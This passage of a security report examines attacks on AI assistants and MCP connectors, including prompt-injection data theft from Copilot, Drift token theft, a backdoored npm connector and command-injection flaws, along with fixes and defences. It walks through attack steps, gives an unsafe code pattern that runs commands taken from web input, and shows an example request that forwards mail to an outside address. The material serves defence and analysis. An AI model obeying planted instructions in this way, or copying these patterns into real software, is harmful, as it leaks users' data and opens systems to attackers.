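Cato's researchers directed AI agents to search for these weaknesses. The agents wrote test cases, studied Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Radware's team had done similar work by hand in 2025. Automation makes it easier to keep trying, which weakens any defence that depends on most attempts failing.

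The team reported its findings to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, gives the repair dates as 17 September for the code interpreter, 11 November for generated files and 15 November for the Bing image. He also quotes Cato as saying that "too little progress has been made" in the year and a half since EchoLeak. Cato sells AI security and has an interest in that conclusion, but its own results give some support for it, because the same team again got data out of the same product with the same kind of email.

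### What the repairs changed

The repair times in this table are calculated from the published dates. Cato gave only a date range for its three reports, so those rows show a range.

| Attack | Entry point | Way out | Clicks needed | Days from report to repair | Known exploitation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Unread email | Image fetched through Teams | None | About 160 at most | None, according to Microsoft |
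| ShadowLeak | Email | Web address opened on OpenAI's servers | None | About 50 | None reported |
| ZombieAgent, email version | Email | One fixed address per character | None | 81 | None reported |
| SearchLeak | Link to a Microsoft site | Image fetched through Bing | One | Report date not published | None, according to Microsoft |
| ReLeak, image | Unread email | Image fetched through Bing | None | 87 to 109 | None known to Cato |
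| ReLeak, files | Unread email | Link in a saved file | None | 83 to 105 | None known to Cato |
| ReLeak, code | Unread email | Program that contacts an outside server | None | 28 to 50 | None known to Cato |

The repairs whose details are public worked by stopping data from getting out. OpenAI's response to ShadowLeak limited which addresses ChatGPT could open, but the agent could still read a malicious email and be misled by it. Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026) likewise describes Microsoft's ReLeak fixes as closing the three routes by which data left. Microsoft changed Copilot's defences after EchoLeak, but Antipov reports that Copilot could still treat instructions from an untrusted source as part of its task.

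There is a good case for focusing on blocking the routes by which data can leave. Nobody knows how to make a model reliably ignore planted text, but a sandbox with no network connection keeps data in even when the model is completely deceived. A theft also needs every step to succeed, so one dependable barrier is enough to stop it. By that standard, the code interpreter flaw was the most serious of the ReLeak flaws, because Microsoft had promised such a barrier in writing and customers could reasonably have relied on it.

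As the product gains features, it also gains ways for data to get out. Copilot could leak data through links in 2024 and through images in 2025. By 2026 it could also write files and run programs, and each ability gave researchers another route. Some routes were hard to recognise because the component that contacted the attacker was Teams, Bing or a background process working normally. Closing these routes also does not stop attacks that send no data out, such as Radware's false medical history.

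The models resisted some attempts. Deep research refused Radware's blunt requests, and Copilot ignored direct commands in Cato's tests. Vendors' filters and training probably stop many careless attackers, but the published attacks come from people who kept trying after the first refusal, and they do not show how many attempts fail.

Microsoft and OpenAI also arguably handled these flaws better than the makers of earlier technologies handled theirs. They run the assistants on their own servers, so a repair reaches every customer at once. Companies had nothing to install after ReLeak, and no old, flawed copies of Copilot remain in use. Users of MOVEit or old versions of Word had no such protection. Even the slowest repair in the table took less than six months, but an attacker who had found the flaw independently could have used it throughout that time without customers knowing they were at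 risk.

The absence of known victims is some evidence that no data was stolen, but this evidence is stronger in some cases than in others. Microsoft could examine its own systems before it said that EchoLeak had affected no customers. Cato could report only what it had heard. For ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent, the requests came from OpenAI's servers, so a victim's employer would have had little chance of noticing a theft.

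## August 2025 to November 2026: stolen access tokens and unsafe connector software

An attacker who steals a connector's access token can use it directly, without planting instructions in anyone's email. Someone who controls the connector's code can do much the same. Both kinds of attack are older than language models, and in August 2025 one such attack exposed hundreds of companies.

### Salesloft Drift

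Drift is an AI chat assistant that companies put on their websites to turn visitors into sales leads. Its owner, Salesloft, stored the tokens that connected Drift to each customer's Salesforce records and often to other services. Salesloft confirmed that attackers had access to its development platform between March and June 2025 and stole those tokens, according to *Salesloft Drift supply chain attack leads to widespread data theft*, a client alert from the law firm McDermott.

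The attackers were using them by 8 August. Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025), in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift*, Google's report on the campaign, describe what they did:

1. They presented a company's Drift token to Salesforce.
2. They counted the company's customer accounts, sales opportunities, users and support cases.
3. They exported records in bulk. One query that Google published asks for up to 10,000 support cases.
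4. They searched the exported data for passwords and for keys to cloud services such as Amazon's and Snowflake's.
5. They deleted the query jobs, but this did not affect Salesforce's logs.

Google's team thinks the attackers mainly wanted the credentials in step 4, which could open further systems.

Multi-factor login, which asks for a second proof of identity such as a code from a phone, did not help because it applies only when a person signs in. The person who connected Drift to Salesforce had already signed in, and anyone who had the resulting token could use it without signing in.

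Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 "potentially impacted" organisations. Krebs on Security (2025) reports that the attackers also took tokens for hundreds of other services that customers could connect to Salesloft's products, including Slack, Microsoft Azure and OpenAI. On 9 August they used some of these tokens to read mail in what Google called a very small number of Workspace accounts. They could reach only the individual accounts connected to Drift. Salesloft and Salesforce cancelled all of Drift's Salesforce tokens on 20 August, 12 days after the first known theft.

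The attackers didn't have to deceive Drift's model, and the same attack could have hit a sales tool with no AI in it. But an assistant becomes more useful as customers connect more services to it, and its maker then holds the tokens for all of them. Joshua Wright of the security firm Counter Hack coined the term "authorization sprawl" for the wider problem. He described attackers who move between systems with legitimate tokens and often go unnoticed because they stay within a real user's existing access.

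In a separate campaign that summer, callers took companies' Salesforce data without stealing tokens, by talking employees into connecting a malicious application to their employer's Salesforce account. Pawn Storm had done much the same ten years before, when it offered Gmail users a malicious application called "Google Defender". Krebs lists Adidas, Allianz Life and Qantas among the companies affected, and the callers also got into one of Google's Salesforce databases.

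### An employee's AI tool at Vercel

Vercel, which hosts websites and apps, disclosed a break-in on 19 April 2026. It traced the cause to Context.ai, an outside AI tool that one employee used, according to the summary of its bulletin in Auxiliar AI's *Vercel security incident*. The attacker took over that employee's Google Workspace account through the tool, then used the account to get into Vercel's internal systems.

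Trend Micro says the attack began around February, when password-stealing malware infected Context.ai. The attacker then used Context.ai's OAuth tokens for Google Workspace. Vercel's chief executive, Guillermo Rauch, confirmed this sequence of events and named the tool.

The attacker reached environment variables for a limited group of customer projects. These variables are settings a program reads when it starts, and they often include credentials. Vercel found no evidence that anyone had read the variables marked as sensitive, according to VPNCentral's *Vercel confirms breach after Context.ai compromise exposed some customer secrets*. TechNadu's *Vercel Investigation Discovers More Compromised Accounts in Context.ai Breach* reports that Vercel later found a small number of further compromised accounts, as well as some customer accounts that attackers seemed to have entered in unrelated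 incidents.

Vercel was exposed through a tool that a single employee had chosen, whereas Drift's customers had adopted Drift as companies. Google's checks on new applications would not necessarily have caught the problem, since a legitimate application can pass them and have its tokens stolen later.

By November 2026, attackers were also stealing tokens for AI services themselves. *AI-Linked Breaches Mount as WorkOS, Northflank, Trigger.dev Disclose Hacks* (Arghire, 2026) calls one use of these tokens "LLM-jacking", which means running models on someone else's account.

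### postmark-mcp: one added line

Postmark is a service that sends emails such as receipts and password resets for apps. In September 2025, someone published a connector for it called postmark-mcp on npm, a public library of JavaScript packages. Postmark was not involved and had not published a connector of its own there.

The author copied the code from Postmark's genuine connector on GitHub. The first 15 versions of the copy worked properly, but version 1.0.16 added one line that blind-copied every outgoing message to the author's address. Koi, a firm that sells protection against malicious packages, found the problem.

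An agent using the connector would not have noticed the extra address, because the connector added it after the agent had called the mail-sending tool with the right recipient and text. An approval window showing the agent's request would also have looked correct. Invariant's proposed fingerprint of the tool description would not have helped either, because the author could change the code without changing the description. Users could have protected themselves by staying on a version they had checked.

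Koi's estimate of 3,000 to 15,000 stolen emails a day is openly a guess. Koi started with 1,500 downloads a week, assumed that a fifth were in active use, and treated those as 300 organisations each sending 10 to 50 emails a day. Paubox puts total downloads at 1,643, so Koi's weekly figure is nearly as high as the total for the package's whole life. Downloads also include repeat installations and automated copies, and nobody has published a count of the people who sent mail through the package.

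According to ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (2025), the author uploaded the package on 15 September and the malicious version on 17 September. Koi also describes users coming to trust the tool before it became malicious, but these dates leave little time for that. OSV's public warning, *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), followed on 26 September. The author deleted the package from npm after Koi contacted him, but that did not remove it from computers where it was already installed.

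### MCP Inspector: a web page that could run commands

The developer behind postmark-mcp meant to steal, but connector software written in good faith can also let an attacker in, as Anthropic's own testing tool did in 2025.

Developers use MCP Inspector to test connectors before release. It has a browser page and a proxy, a small program on the developer's machine that passes messages between the page and the connector. The proxy can start a local connector by running a command. OSV's *CVE-2025-49596* (2025) records that the proxy did not check who was sending it requests, and rates the flaw's severity 9.4 out of 10.

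Lumelsky (2025), in *Critical RCE Vulnerability in Anthropic MCP Inspector*, explains how an attacker could exploit this. Browsers are supposed to keep public websites from reaching programs on the user's own machine, but major browsers had for 19 years mishandled a network address that leads back to that machine. If a developer visited a malicious page while the Inspector was running, the page could send a command to that address, and the proxy would run it. Lumelsky's firm, Oligo Security, also found copies of the Inspector open to the internet, which an attacker could reach directly.

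Oligo reported the flaw on 18 April 2025 and learned that another researcher had done so on 26 March. GitLab's *CVE-2025-49596* (2025) credits Rémy Marot of the security company Tenable. Anthropic fixed the flaw in version 0.14.1, where the proxy requires a secret token for each session and refuses requests from unfamiliar websites. The proxy can still start programs, but those websites can no longer use it to do so. Lumelsky reports no victims.

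### The dispute over starting local servers

In April 2026, the security firm OX Security argued that the feature behind the Inspector flaw was itself unsafe. AI applications use this feature, called STDIO (standard input/output), to start local MCP servers by running a command. Anthropic publishes code libraries that do this.

The library runs whatever command it receives. If the command does not start an MCP server, the library returns an error, but by then the command has run. OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* contrasts safe and unsafe uses, roughly as follows:

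```python
# Safe: the developer has fixed the command
StdioServerParameters(command="python", args=["myapp.py"])

# Unsafe: a visitor to a website supplies the command
StdioServerParameters(command=form["command"], args=form["args"])
```

OX ran its own commands on six live platforms with real users. On one of them, Letta, the settings page offered only remote connectors, but the server still accepted local ones, so the researchers altered a request in transit to use one. LangFlow, a tool for building AI applications, gave a session token to anyone who asked. OX found 915 copies of LangFlow on the public internet, although its makers had designed it to run locally.

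Attackers could exploit this problem through prompt injection in Windsurf, a code editor with an AI agent. The agent could edit the file that lists the user's connectors. A web page with planted instructions could make the agent add an entry, and Windsurf would run the new command without asking the user. Similar attacks on Cursor, Claude Code and Google's Gemini-CLI needed some action from the user.

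**Source of the 200,000 figure.** OX Security's *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers* reports more than 7,000 publicly accessible servers and "up to 200,000 vulnerable instances in total". The smaller figure is a count, which flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*, by a blogger who promotes his own rival tool, gives as 7,374 servers found through Shodan, a search engine for internet-connected machines. OX extrapolated the larger figure from those servers, according to VentureBeat's *200,000 MCP servers expose a command execution flaw*. The larger figure is about 27 times the smaller, and neither OX's announcement nor VentureBeat's article explains the ratio.

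VentureBeat's headline nevertheless presents the estimate as a count. *MCP STDIO RCE, The Agent Execution Boundary Failed*, from Penligent, another security vendor, points out that OX has not shown that 200,000 internet-facing servers are open to attack. The 7,000 servers that VentureBeat describes as public with STDIO active are not necessarily open to attack either, because an attacker also needs some way to supply the command. The six platforms are much better evidence than either total.

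**Anthropic's reply.** OX contacted Anthropic on 7 January 2026. According to OX's full report, as quoted by flyingpenguin, Anthropic replied that the behaviour OX reported was an explicit part of how such servers work and that "we believe that this design does represent a secure default". VentureBeat got no answer from Anthropic and treats the word "expected" as the company's only statement on the record. Nine days after OX's first message, Anthropic updated its security guidance to advise caution with STDIO adapters, but it did not change the code. The makers of LangChain and FastMCP, two libraries that build on the same feature, also declined to treat it as a flaw in their software.

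Anthropic has a reasonable case, because the feature exists to start programs and a person who can edit a computer's connector settings can normally run programs there anyway. The project's security policy, as summarised on a Model Context Protocol site, similarly states that malicious local servers can run code because the user's application has already started them. OX's finding gives an attacker no new abilities on a laptop whose owner writes her own settings.

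That reasoning fails when somebody else can write the settings, as website visitors could on LangFlow and a deceived agent could in Windsurf. OX blames the design, arguing that thousands of developers will not all check their inputs correctly. Its best example is Flowise, another tool for building AI applications, whose developers had seen the danger and allowed only certain commands. One permitted program had an option to run any other command, so OX bypassed the check in one step.

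The Flowise case is also evidence against one of OX's proposed remedies, a list of permitted commands in Anthropic's libraries. Most local connectors start through a general-purpose program such as Python, and a list that permits Python permits almost anything. OX also proposes a setting that developers would have to switch on before the library ran arbitrary commands, which would at least warn them. But the library receives the same text whether a developer or a visitor wrote it, so it would have to require the setting for legitimate connectors too, and many developers might switch it on and forget about it. OX's advice to run connectors in a sandbox looks sounder, because a sandbox limits the damage from a bad command without having to recognise it. OX sells tools that detect the unsafe pattern.

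Makers of several affected products, including LiteLLM and DocsGPT, released fixes. As of 1 May 2026, VentureBeat could not confirm a fix for Windsurf. OX also submitted a harmless test connector to 11 public directories of MCP servers, and nine accepted it, which suggests that they would also have accepted a malicious one like postmark-mcp.

### Why the known harm is so uneven

| Attack | What the attacker needed | Known real-world harm |
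|---|---|---|
| Salesloft Drift, 2025 | Tokens held by one supplier | Data theft; more than 700 organisations potentially affected |
| Vercel, 2026 | Tokens held by an employee's AI tool | Settings exposed for a limited group of customers |
| postmark-mcp, 2025 | Control of a published connector | A working backdoor in a package with 1,643 downloads; no victim named |
| MCP Inspector, 2025 | A developer's visit to a web page | None reported |
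| STDIO commands, 2026 | A way to supply the command | None reported beyond OX's tests |
| EchoLeak, ShadowLeak and ReLeak, 2025–26 | An email that the assistant would read | None reported |

In the cases covered here, stolen tokens have done far more damage than prompt injection. Part of the difference comes from how each kind of attack becomes public. The Drift theft became news because someone had already taken the data. Researchers found the prompt-injection flaws and reported them privately, and vendors fixed them before publication, so a list of such reports would include few victims even if there were many.

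Stolen tokens and planted emails also leave different evidence. Larsen and colleagues published the network addresses and software names that the thieves had used, so companies could search their Salesforce logs for them. Many of the addresses belonged to Tor, a network that hides where a connection comes from and that Drift would have had little reason to use. When an attacker steers an assistant with a planted email, the request comes from the usual software at its usual address. An investigator would have to find the email and connect it to the request, and for an attack such as ShadowLeak, only OpenAI would hold the relevant logs.

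Companies do not always disclose what they know quickly. Krebs on Security reports that Salesloft's first notice, on 20 August, asked customers to reconnect Drift to Salesforce but did not mention stolen tokens. Google, which did not use Drift, published the details six days later. Several companies had seen part of the Drift theft, so Salesloft could not have kept it quiet for long. With Copilot or ChatGPT, there may be no second company able to disclose a problem. Salesforce's silence about ForcedLeak is one example.

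Disclosure habits probably don't explain the whole difference, because a criminal who can get tokens has little reason to use planted emails. A stolen token works every time and gives access to a company's records in bulk, and one break-in at Salesloft yielded tokens for hundreds of companies. A planted email may fail, usually reaches one person's data at a time, and stops working once the vendor fixes the flaw.

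Large thefts are also hard to keep secret, because criminals often announce them to extort money. The group behind that summer's phone calls appeared to be preparing a website for leaked data. If anyone had used prompt injection to steal from 700 companies, some sign of it would probably have surfaced by now. But a spy who used it to read a few dozen mailboxes, without demanding money, could easily have gone unnoticed.

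## March 2025 to July 2026: adding identity and permission checks

A thief can use a stolen access token because the service that receives it checks little about who is presenting it. MCP's maintainers have added such checks in four versions of the protocol since March 2025, but authorization is optional in all four.

| Version | Time since launch | Main additions | Left optional |
|---|---|---|---|
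| 26 March 2025 | 4 months | A login framework based on OAuth | Authorization as a whole |
| 18 June 2025 | Almost 7 months | Connectors must name their authorization server, accept only tokens meant for them and never pass tokens on | Authorization as a whole |
| 25 November 2025 | 12 months | A new way for applications to identify themselves; extensions for machine logins and company control | Authorization as a whole; both extensions |
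| 28 July 2026 | 20 months | Applications must check which authorization server sent a reply, and keep separate credentials for each | Authorization as a whole; naming the sender in the reply |

The requirements therefore apply only to remote connectors whose makers choose to support authorization. A local connector should instead take its credentials from settings on the user's machine.

### Why the checks came late

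In Stack Overflow's *No need for Ctrl+C when you have MCP* (2026), David Soria Parra, who created MCP with Justin Spahr-Summers at Anthropic, explains the delay. The earliest design connected an application only to programs on the same computer. Those programs already had the user's full access, so a login would have added little. Remote services did need a login, so the maintainers turned to OAuth. But OAuth is mostly designed for applications and servers that have been set up to work together in advance, while MCP lets any application connect to any server, so the maintainers had to extend OAuth.

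This explains the early design better than it explains the launch, because the first published version already allowed remote servers. An early reply in *Authentication*, a discussion on the project's GitHub page, says the team had thought about the problem, but "definitely not enough to bake something into the spec yet".

MCP's two creators gave another reason for caution in an April 2025 interview with Latent Space, saying that a protocol's designers can easily add a feature but can hardly ever remove one. When the interviewer asked about letting a user limit an assistant to certain kinds of email, the creators saw the appeal but first wanted a practical example in which the existing rules failed. MCP still leaves each connector's maker to define the connector's scopes.

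The MCP team knew that the initial release lacked authentication and released it anyway. Lane (2025), in *No Auth on Initial MCP Was Not A Bug*, argued that this was a feature and that commentators were wrong to treat it as an oversight. But the reply on GitHub describes unfinished work, and the maintainers had published a login framework a month before Lane wrote.

According to *Simplifying MCP*, from the makers of the http4k programming library, many people found that first framework too complicated because each connector had to issue tokens as well as accept them. A developer who only wanted to offer access to a project tracker also had to build a login system. The June 2025 version separated the two jobs, so a connector could rely on an existing authorization server to issue tokens.

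### One login, step by step

Suppose a user adds a project tracker's remote connector to her AI application, which at first knows only the connector's address. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) and Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Server Discovery* (2026) set out what happens next under the July 2026 rules:

1. The application sends the connector a request without a token. The connector refuses it and usually points to a document about itself.
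2. The application reads that document, which names the connector's authorization server.
3. The application fetches the authorization server's own description and checks that the name in it, called the issuer, matches the address it used. If a description from `attacker.example` gives the issuer as `honest.example`, the application must reject it. Otherwise it records the issuer.
4. The application identifies itself to the authorization server.
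5. The application opens the sign-in page in the user's browser, with a request that names the connector she wants to use.
6. The user signs in and approves. Her browser returns to the application with a single-use code and, in most cases, the issuer's name.
7. The application compares that name with the one it recorded. If they match, it exchanges the code for an access token.
8. The application sends the token with every request, and the connector checks each time that the token was meant for it.

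Step 4 caused trouble for more than a year. Parecki (2025) explains that in ordinary OAuth, a developer registers an application with a service by hand and receives an ID for it. Nobody can do that for every pairing of application and connector. The June 2025 version recommended letting applications register automatically, which meant authorization servers had to accept registrations from unknown applications.

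Since November 2025, the maintainers have recommended that an application use a web address as its ID, and the authorization server reads the application's details there. The July version formally deprecates automatic registration, though it still works. Descope, which sells login software, points out in *What the July 2026 MCP Revision Means for Identity* that an application's identity now comes from control of a domain. Pawn Storm, for example, could not have given its fake "Google Defender" an address on Google's domain. It could still have registered a similar-looking domain, so the authorization server has to decide which domains to trust.

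### Why a token should work at only one connector

A malicious connector can name the tracker's real authorization server as its own in step 2. The user then sees a real sign-in page and approves. If the resulting token worked with any service, the application would send it to the malicious connector, which could use it to open the user's tracker.

Since June 2025, applications have had to name the connector in both the sign-in request and the token request, and the authorization server can write that name into the token. Each connector must reject tokens meant for any other. Some authorization servers do not support this, though applications send them the name anyway, so the protection depends on which server is used. It also does not stop thieves from stealing a token after a genuine login and using it on the service it was meant for, as they did with Drift's Salesforce tokens.

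The June 2025 Model Context Protocol rules also forbid a connector to pass on the token it receives. Many connectors call another company's service, and forwarding the user's token would be the easiest way to log in there. But that service might accept the token as if the connector had already checked it, or treat the request as the connector's own, and either mistake would make the connector a confused deputy. The connector must instead obtain a separate token from the other service.

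The June version did not explain how to handle this second login. In November 2025, the developer peteski22 complained in *MCP's identity crisis* (2025) that there was no standard method and that even official connectors could not follow the June version's advice. The next version, released eight days later, lets a connector send the user to a web page during a task to sign in to the other service directly.

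### Checking which server replied

The issuer check in step 7 comes from the OAuth standard RFC 9207 and prevents a "mix-up" attack. An AI application may deal with a dozen authorization servers at once. *MCP's Auth Hardening*, by the security vendor Tigera, explains that an attacker only needs to make the application attribute a reply to the wrong server and does not have to break any encryption.

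Suppose the user adds a malicious connector that has its own authorization server. The attack can then work like this:

1. The application records the attacker's server as the issuer and opens its sign-in page.
2. That page redirects the browser to the tracker's genuine sign-in page.
3. The user approves, and the genuine server sends a code back to the application.
4. The application thinks the code came from the attacker's server, so it sends the code there to exchange it for a token.
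5. The attacker exchanges the code at the genuine server and gains access to the user's tracker.

If the reply at step 3 names the genuine server, the application detects that the name does not match its record and stops. Under the July rules, the application must make this comparison whenever a reply includes a name. It must also reject a reply without a name if the authorization server has declared that it will include one. But if the server has made no such declaration and sends no name, the application continues, so older authorization servers remain exposed.

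The maintainers expect to require the name in a future version. They aim to publish the next version on 30 March 2027, according to Model Context Protocol's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026).

### When the company approves the connection

In the login above, the user decides whether to connect. In a company, each employee therefore approves each connector separately, and the security team has no central list. An employee can also connect a personal account to a work tool by mistake.

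Enterprise-Managed Authorization gives the decision to the company. It is an optional extension that became stable on 18 June 2026, and it relies on the company's identity provider, the service through which employees sign in to their work software. Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization* (2026) and Descope describe the process:

1. An administrator sets out which groups of employees may use which connectors.
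2. An employee signs in to the AI application through the identity provider, as usual.
3. The application asks the identity provider for access to a connector. If the company's policy allows it, the identity provider issues a signed statement of who the employee is.
4. The connector's authorization server checks the statement and issues an access token.

The employee never sees a consent page. Okta was the first identity provider to support the extension. Anthropic added it to Claude, and Microsoft's code editor Visual Studio Code supports it. The first connectors came from companies including Asana, Atlassian and Supabase.

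Administrators can now see and withdraw access in one place, which would help after a token theft. The extension would not by itself have prevented the Vercel break-in, where an employee's outside tool held its own tokens for Google Workspace. A company has to restrict such tools separately.

The extension also makes connectors easier to switch on. According to Anthropic's *Centrally manage authorization for MCP connectors*, a connector is available the first time someone opens Claude. Employees who would never have installed a mail connector may now have one alongside a web browser and a customer database. Together, these supply all three parts of the lethal trifecta. An administrator could use the same controls to avoid enabling those connectors together. Either way, the administrator approves a connection once and does not see the individual actions that follow.

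### The NSA's findings and the July version

The NSA published its guidance on MCP in May 2026. The maintainers announced the release candidate for the July version that same month, so they had probably settled most of its contents before the guidance came out. The July version still addresses some of the NSA's findings.

| NSA finding | Addressed in July 2026? |
|---|---|
| Authorization is optional, and many connectors have none | No |
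| The protocol does not tie a session to an identity | In part. The protocol no longer has sessions, and connectors that use authorization receive a token with every request. |
| Applications and connectors cannot exchange roles when they connect | In part. A connector can name the scopes a request needs, and companies can apply their own groups and roles through the extension. |
| An approved connector can change without new approval | No |
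| Logs are thin or missing | In part. The tool's name now travels where monitoring software can easily record it, but nobody has to keep a log. |
| The rules do not require tokens to expire or support cancelling them | In part. The rules on renewing access are clearer, but there is no new rule on expiry. |

A connector can enforce roles, such as read-only access, if its maker defines a separate scope for each. When a request needs a scope that the token lacks, the connector rejects the request and returns the name of the missing scope, and the application can then prompt the user to grant it. The July rules do not help enforce roles if the maker defines one scope for everything.

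A more serious gap is that Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* lists no rule requiring an application to seek new approval when a tool's description changes. An application can ask to be notified of changes, but Invariant's WhatsApp attack, which the NSA cites, could still work against an application that followed every rule.

The NSA overstates its finding when it reports that the core specification requires nothing about how tokens expire or get replaced. The June 2025 rules already required authorization servers to replace refresh tokens regularly for applications that cannot store a secret securely, such as those on a user's own computer. However, they only recommended short lifetimes for access tokens, which are the tokens a connector accepts.

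Companies can follow much of the NSA's advice without waiting for a new version. It tells them to:

- choose connectors that someone still maintains, since the MCP project has archived many popular ones
- keep tools that handle public data apart from those that handle sensitive data
- keep an inventory of connectors and their versions
- scan their own networks for connectors that have no login.

For private data, the agency also prefers connectors that run locally. This keeps the data off outside servers but puts the connector's code on the company's own machines, where a malicious connector like postmark-mcp could do more harm. Companies that do this should therefore also follow the agency's advice to sandbox each tool.

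### Who has to do the work

Tabata (2026) argues in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* that established identity practice is mostly enough. He wrote it for the Agentic AI Foundation, which hosts MCP. He says that none of the July changes to authorization introduces a new idea, and that companies have dealt with the same problems in ordinary OAuth systems for years. He recommends that they extend their existing sign-in systems to connectors instead of building new ones. Descope agrees that a mature system needs only a few settings checked, though it sells such systems.

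By contrast, Kale (2026) argues in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential* (VentureBeat) that the July version moves security work from the protocol to the people who implement it. He has built agent systems that use MCP.

Kale's main example is the removal of sessions, which linked one request to the next. A connector that needs to remember something, such as a shopping cart, now gives the model a label called a handle, which the model sends back with later requests. He warns that a planted message could expose a handle or supply a false one, and that anyone with a valid handle can use it.

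According to Descope, the rules forbid a connector from treating a handle as proof of identity, and the guidance is to store each handle together with the user's verified ID. If the connector does this, an attacker who reads a user's handle cannot open her cart from his own account. A planted message can still make her assistant misuse her cart, and no identity check would catch that.

Kale's claim about who does the work is better supported. Descope similarly argues that a session ID obviously needed protection, but a developer may not think to check a cart number because it looks like ordinary data. The November version also supplied an identifier that connectors could use during a login to an outside service, and documentation for two MCP code libraries showed developers how to reuse it to protect against forged logins. The July version removes that identifier, so developers have to create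 and check their own.

The July version does tighten one rule in the protocol itself by letting a connector ask the user for information only while it is handling a request from her application. This makes it harder to send her phishing prompts at arbitrary times.

Tabata's advice suits a bank that already has an identity team better than a lone developer publishing a first connector. The maintainers' release announcement, Model Context Protocol (2026), reports that developers spend most of their integration time on authorization. Many remote servers have no authentication, which suggests that some developers skip this work. Some of those servers may offer only public information and need no login. But Waxell's *MCP Server Authentication* (2026) points out that a server without authentication still complies with the specification, whatever data it holds.

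### A planted email in a compliant system

Suppose a company does all of this correctly. Its mail connector uses the July version with every check in place, and an administrator has approved the connection. An employee asks her assistant to summarise her unread mail. One message contains instructions to forward password resets to an outside address, and the model follows them. In simplified form, the connector receives this:

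```text
Authorization: Bearer [token for this employee and this connector]
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: forward_message

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 12, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {
   "name": "forward_message",
   "arguments": {"message_id": "8841",
                 "to": "archive@outside.example"},
   "_meta": {"io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo":
               {"name": "assistant", "version": "4.1"}}}}
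```

The connector would receive exactly the same request if the employee had asked for the forwarding herself. Of the five questions that make up a request's security context, the checks settle only some:

| Question | Answered? | What the connector can establish |
|---|---|---|
| Who is asking? | Mostly | The authorization server identified the application, but a thief could still present the token. |
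| For whom? | Yes | The company's identity provider verified the employee. |
| For what task? | No | The request names a tool but not the reason for using it. |
| Prompted by whose text? | No | Nothing. |
| Within what limits? | In part | The token works at one connector and within certain scopes, but they may allow far more than this task needs. |

A token that covered only reading would help, because the connector would refuse to forward the message and would identify the missing scope. But the rules recommend that an application acting for a user then request the extra permission. The employee might see a request to let her assistant send mail while it was already working on her mail, with no sign that a stranger's message had prompted it.

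The maintainers could easily add a field for the source of an instruction, but nobody could fill it in reliably. The model's output does not record which passage led to it, and if the model filled in the field itself, the planted text could cause it to name the employee as the source. Soria Parra wants the protocol to help label data so that applications can make better decisions, but software outside the model would have to track the labels.

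*MCPS* (Sharif, 2026), one developer's draft and not a standard, proposes signing every message and every tool definition. The signatures would reveal whether anyone had altered a message on the way, and could expose an unannounced change to a tool. They would not stop the planted request either, because the assistant would sign it too.

### Separate identities for agents

The mail service also records the forwarding request as the employee's own action. If the assistant had its own identity, the service could record that the assistant acted on her behalf and give it fewer permissions than she has.

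*AI AgentTrust & Governance* (2026) traces how MCP's maintainers have moved towards identity checks in stages. In November 2025, an extension let a program obtain a token with its own credentials, without a person signing in. In December, a proposal called Workload Identity Federation went further. The cloud platform that runs an agent would confirm the agent's identity with a short-lived signed statement, so nobody would have to store a long-lived password that a thief could steal.

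In August 2026, the Model Context Protocol maintainers made agent identity one of five priorities for the protocol. They noted that the existing rules assume a person approves access in a browser, while agents increasingly work for users who are not present or delegate work to other agents. They want an agent to be able to pass on only part of its authority. An agent that reads strangers' mail could then hold a token that allows only reading, so it could not forward anything even if a planted message deceived it.

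The same plan includes Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP), an OAuth standard that ties a token to a secret key. The application uses the key to sign each request but never sends it, so a thief who has only the token cannot use it. DPoP is the plan's closest remedy for the Drift theft, but it would have worked only if Salesloft had kept the keys where the thieves could not reach them.

Products from different companies will also have to recognise one another's agents. The OpenID Foundation's *Call for participation* invites companies to test blocking unauthorised agents from a company's systems and verifying an agent that belongs to another organisation.

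As of December 2026, this work is unfinished. Under the maintainers' new release schedule, any proposal not ready for the March 2027 version will wait for a later one.

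## 2025 to 2026: limiting what a deceived model can do

MCP's newer checks establish who is making a request, but they don't distinguish requests the user wanted from those prompted by a planted email. Some developers therefore train models to resist planted instructions, or filter text before a model acts on it. Others assume that an attacker will sometimes deceive the model, and limit what it can do afterwards.

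### Training models and filtering what they read

A developer can train a model on examples in which a tool result contains an instruction, and reward it for carrying on with the user's task. Writing enough good examples by hand is hard. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an automated attacker trained through self-play, in which models improve by competing with one another. OpenAI uses it to find weaknesses in its models before release and trains them against the attacks. By then, its latest models had reached the top of the commonly used robustness tests, so OpenAI could learn little more from those tests.

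Anthropic runs filters alongside the model. In many of its products, "probes" inspect tool results before the model acts on them and flag text that looks like a planted instruction. In its coding agent, Claude Code, the default auto mode adds a classifier that blocks tool calls it considers dangerous. Anthropic argues that an attack would have to defeat both layers independently, since the probes check what the model reads and the classifier checks what it tries to do. But the layers may not fail independently. EchoLeak's email read like ordinary office guidance, and text like that could get past a probe and also make the resulting action look routine to the classifier.

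The most detailed recent figures come from the September 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.1, which reports results from a benchmark run by the security company Gray Swan. People wrote the attacks for public competitions, and Gray Swan kept 1,804 that worked against several models. They cover 37 scenarios in coding, tool use and operating a computer through its screen. The table shows the chance that an attacker succeeds within a given number of attempts.

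| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Among other companies' models, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash did best, with attackers succeeding 9.2% of the time within 15 attempts. The rate for most of the others was between 24% and 53%. Fable 5.1 failed mostly when operating a computer through its screen, where attackers succeeded 4.1% of the time within 15 attempts. In tool use, the category closest to connectors, the rate was 0.0%.

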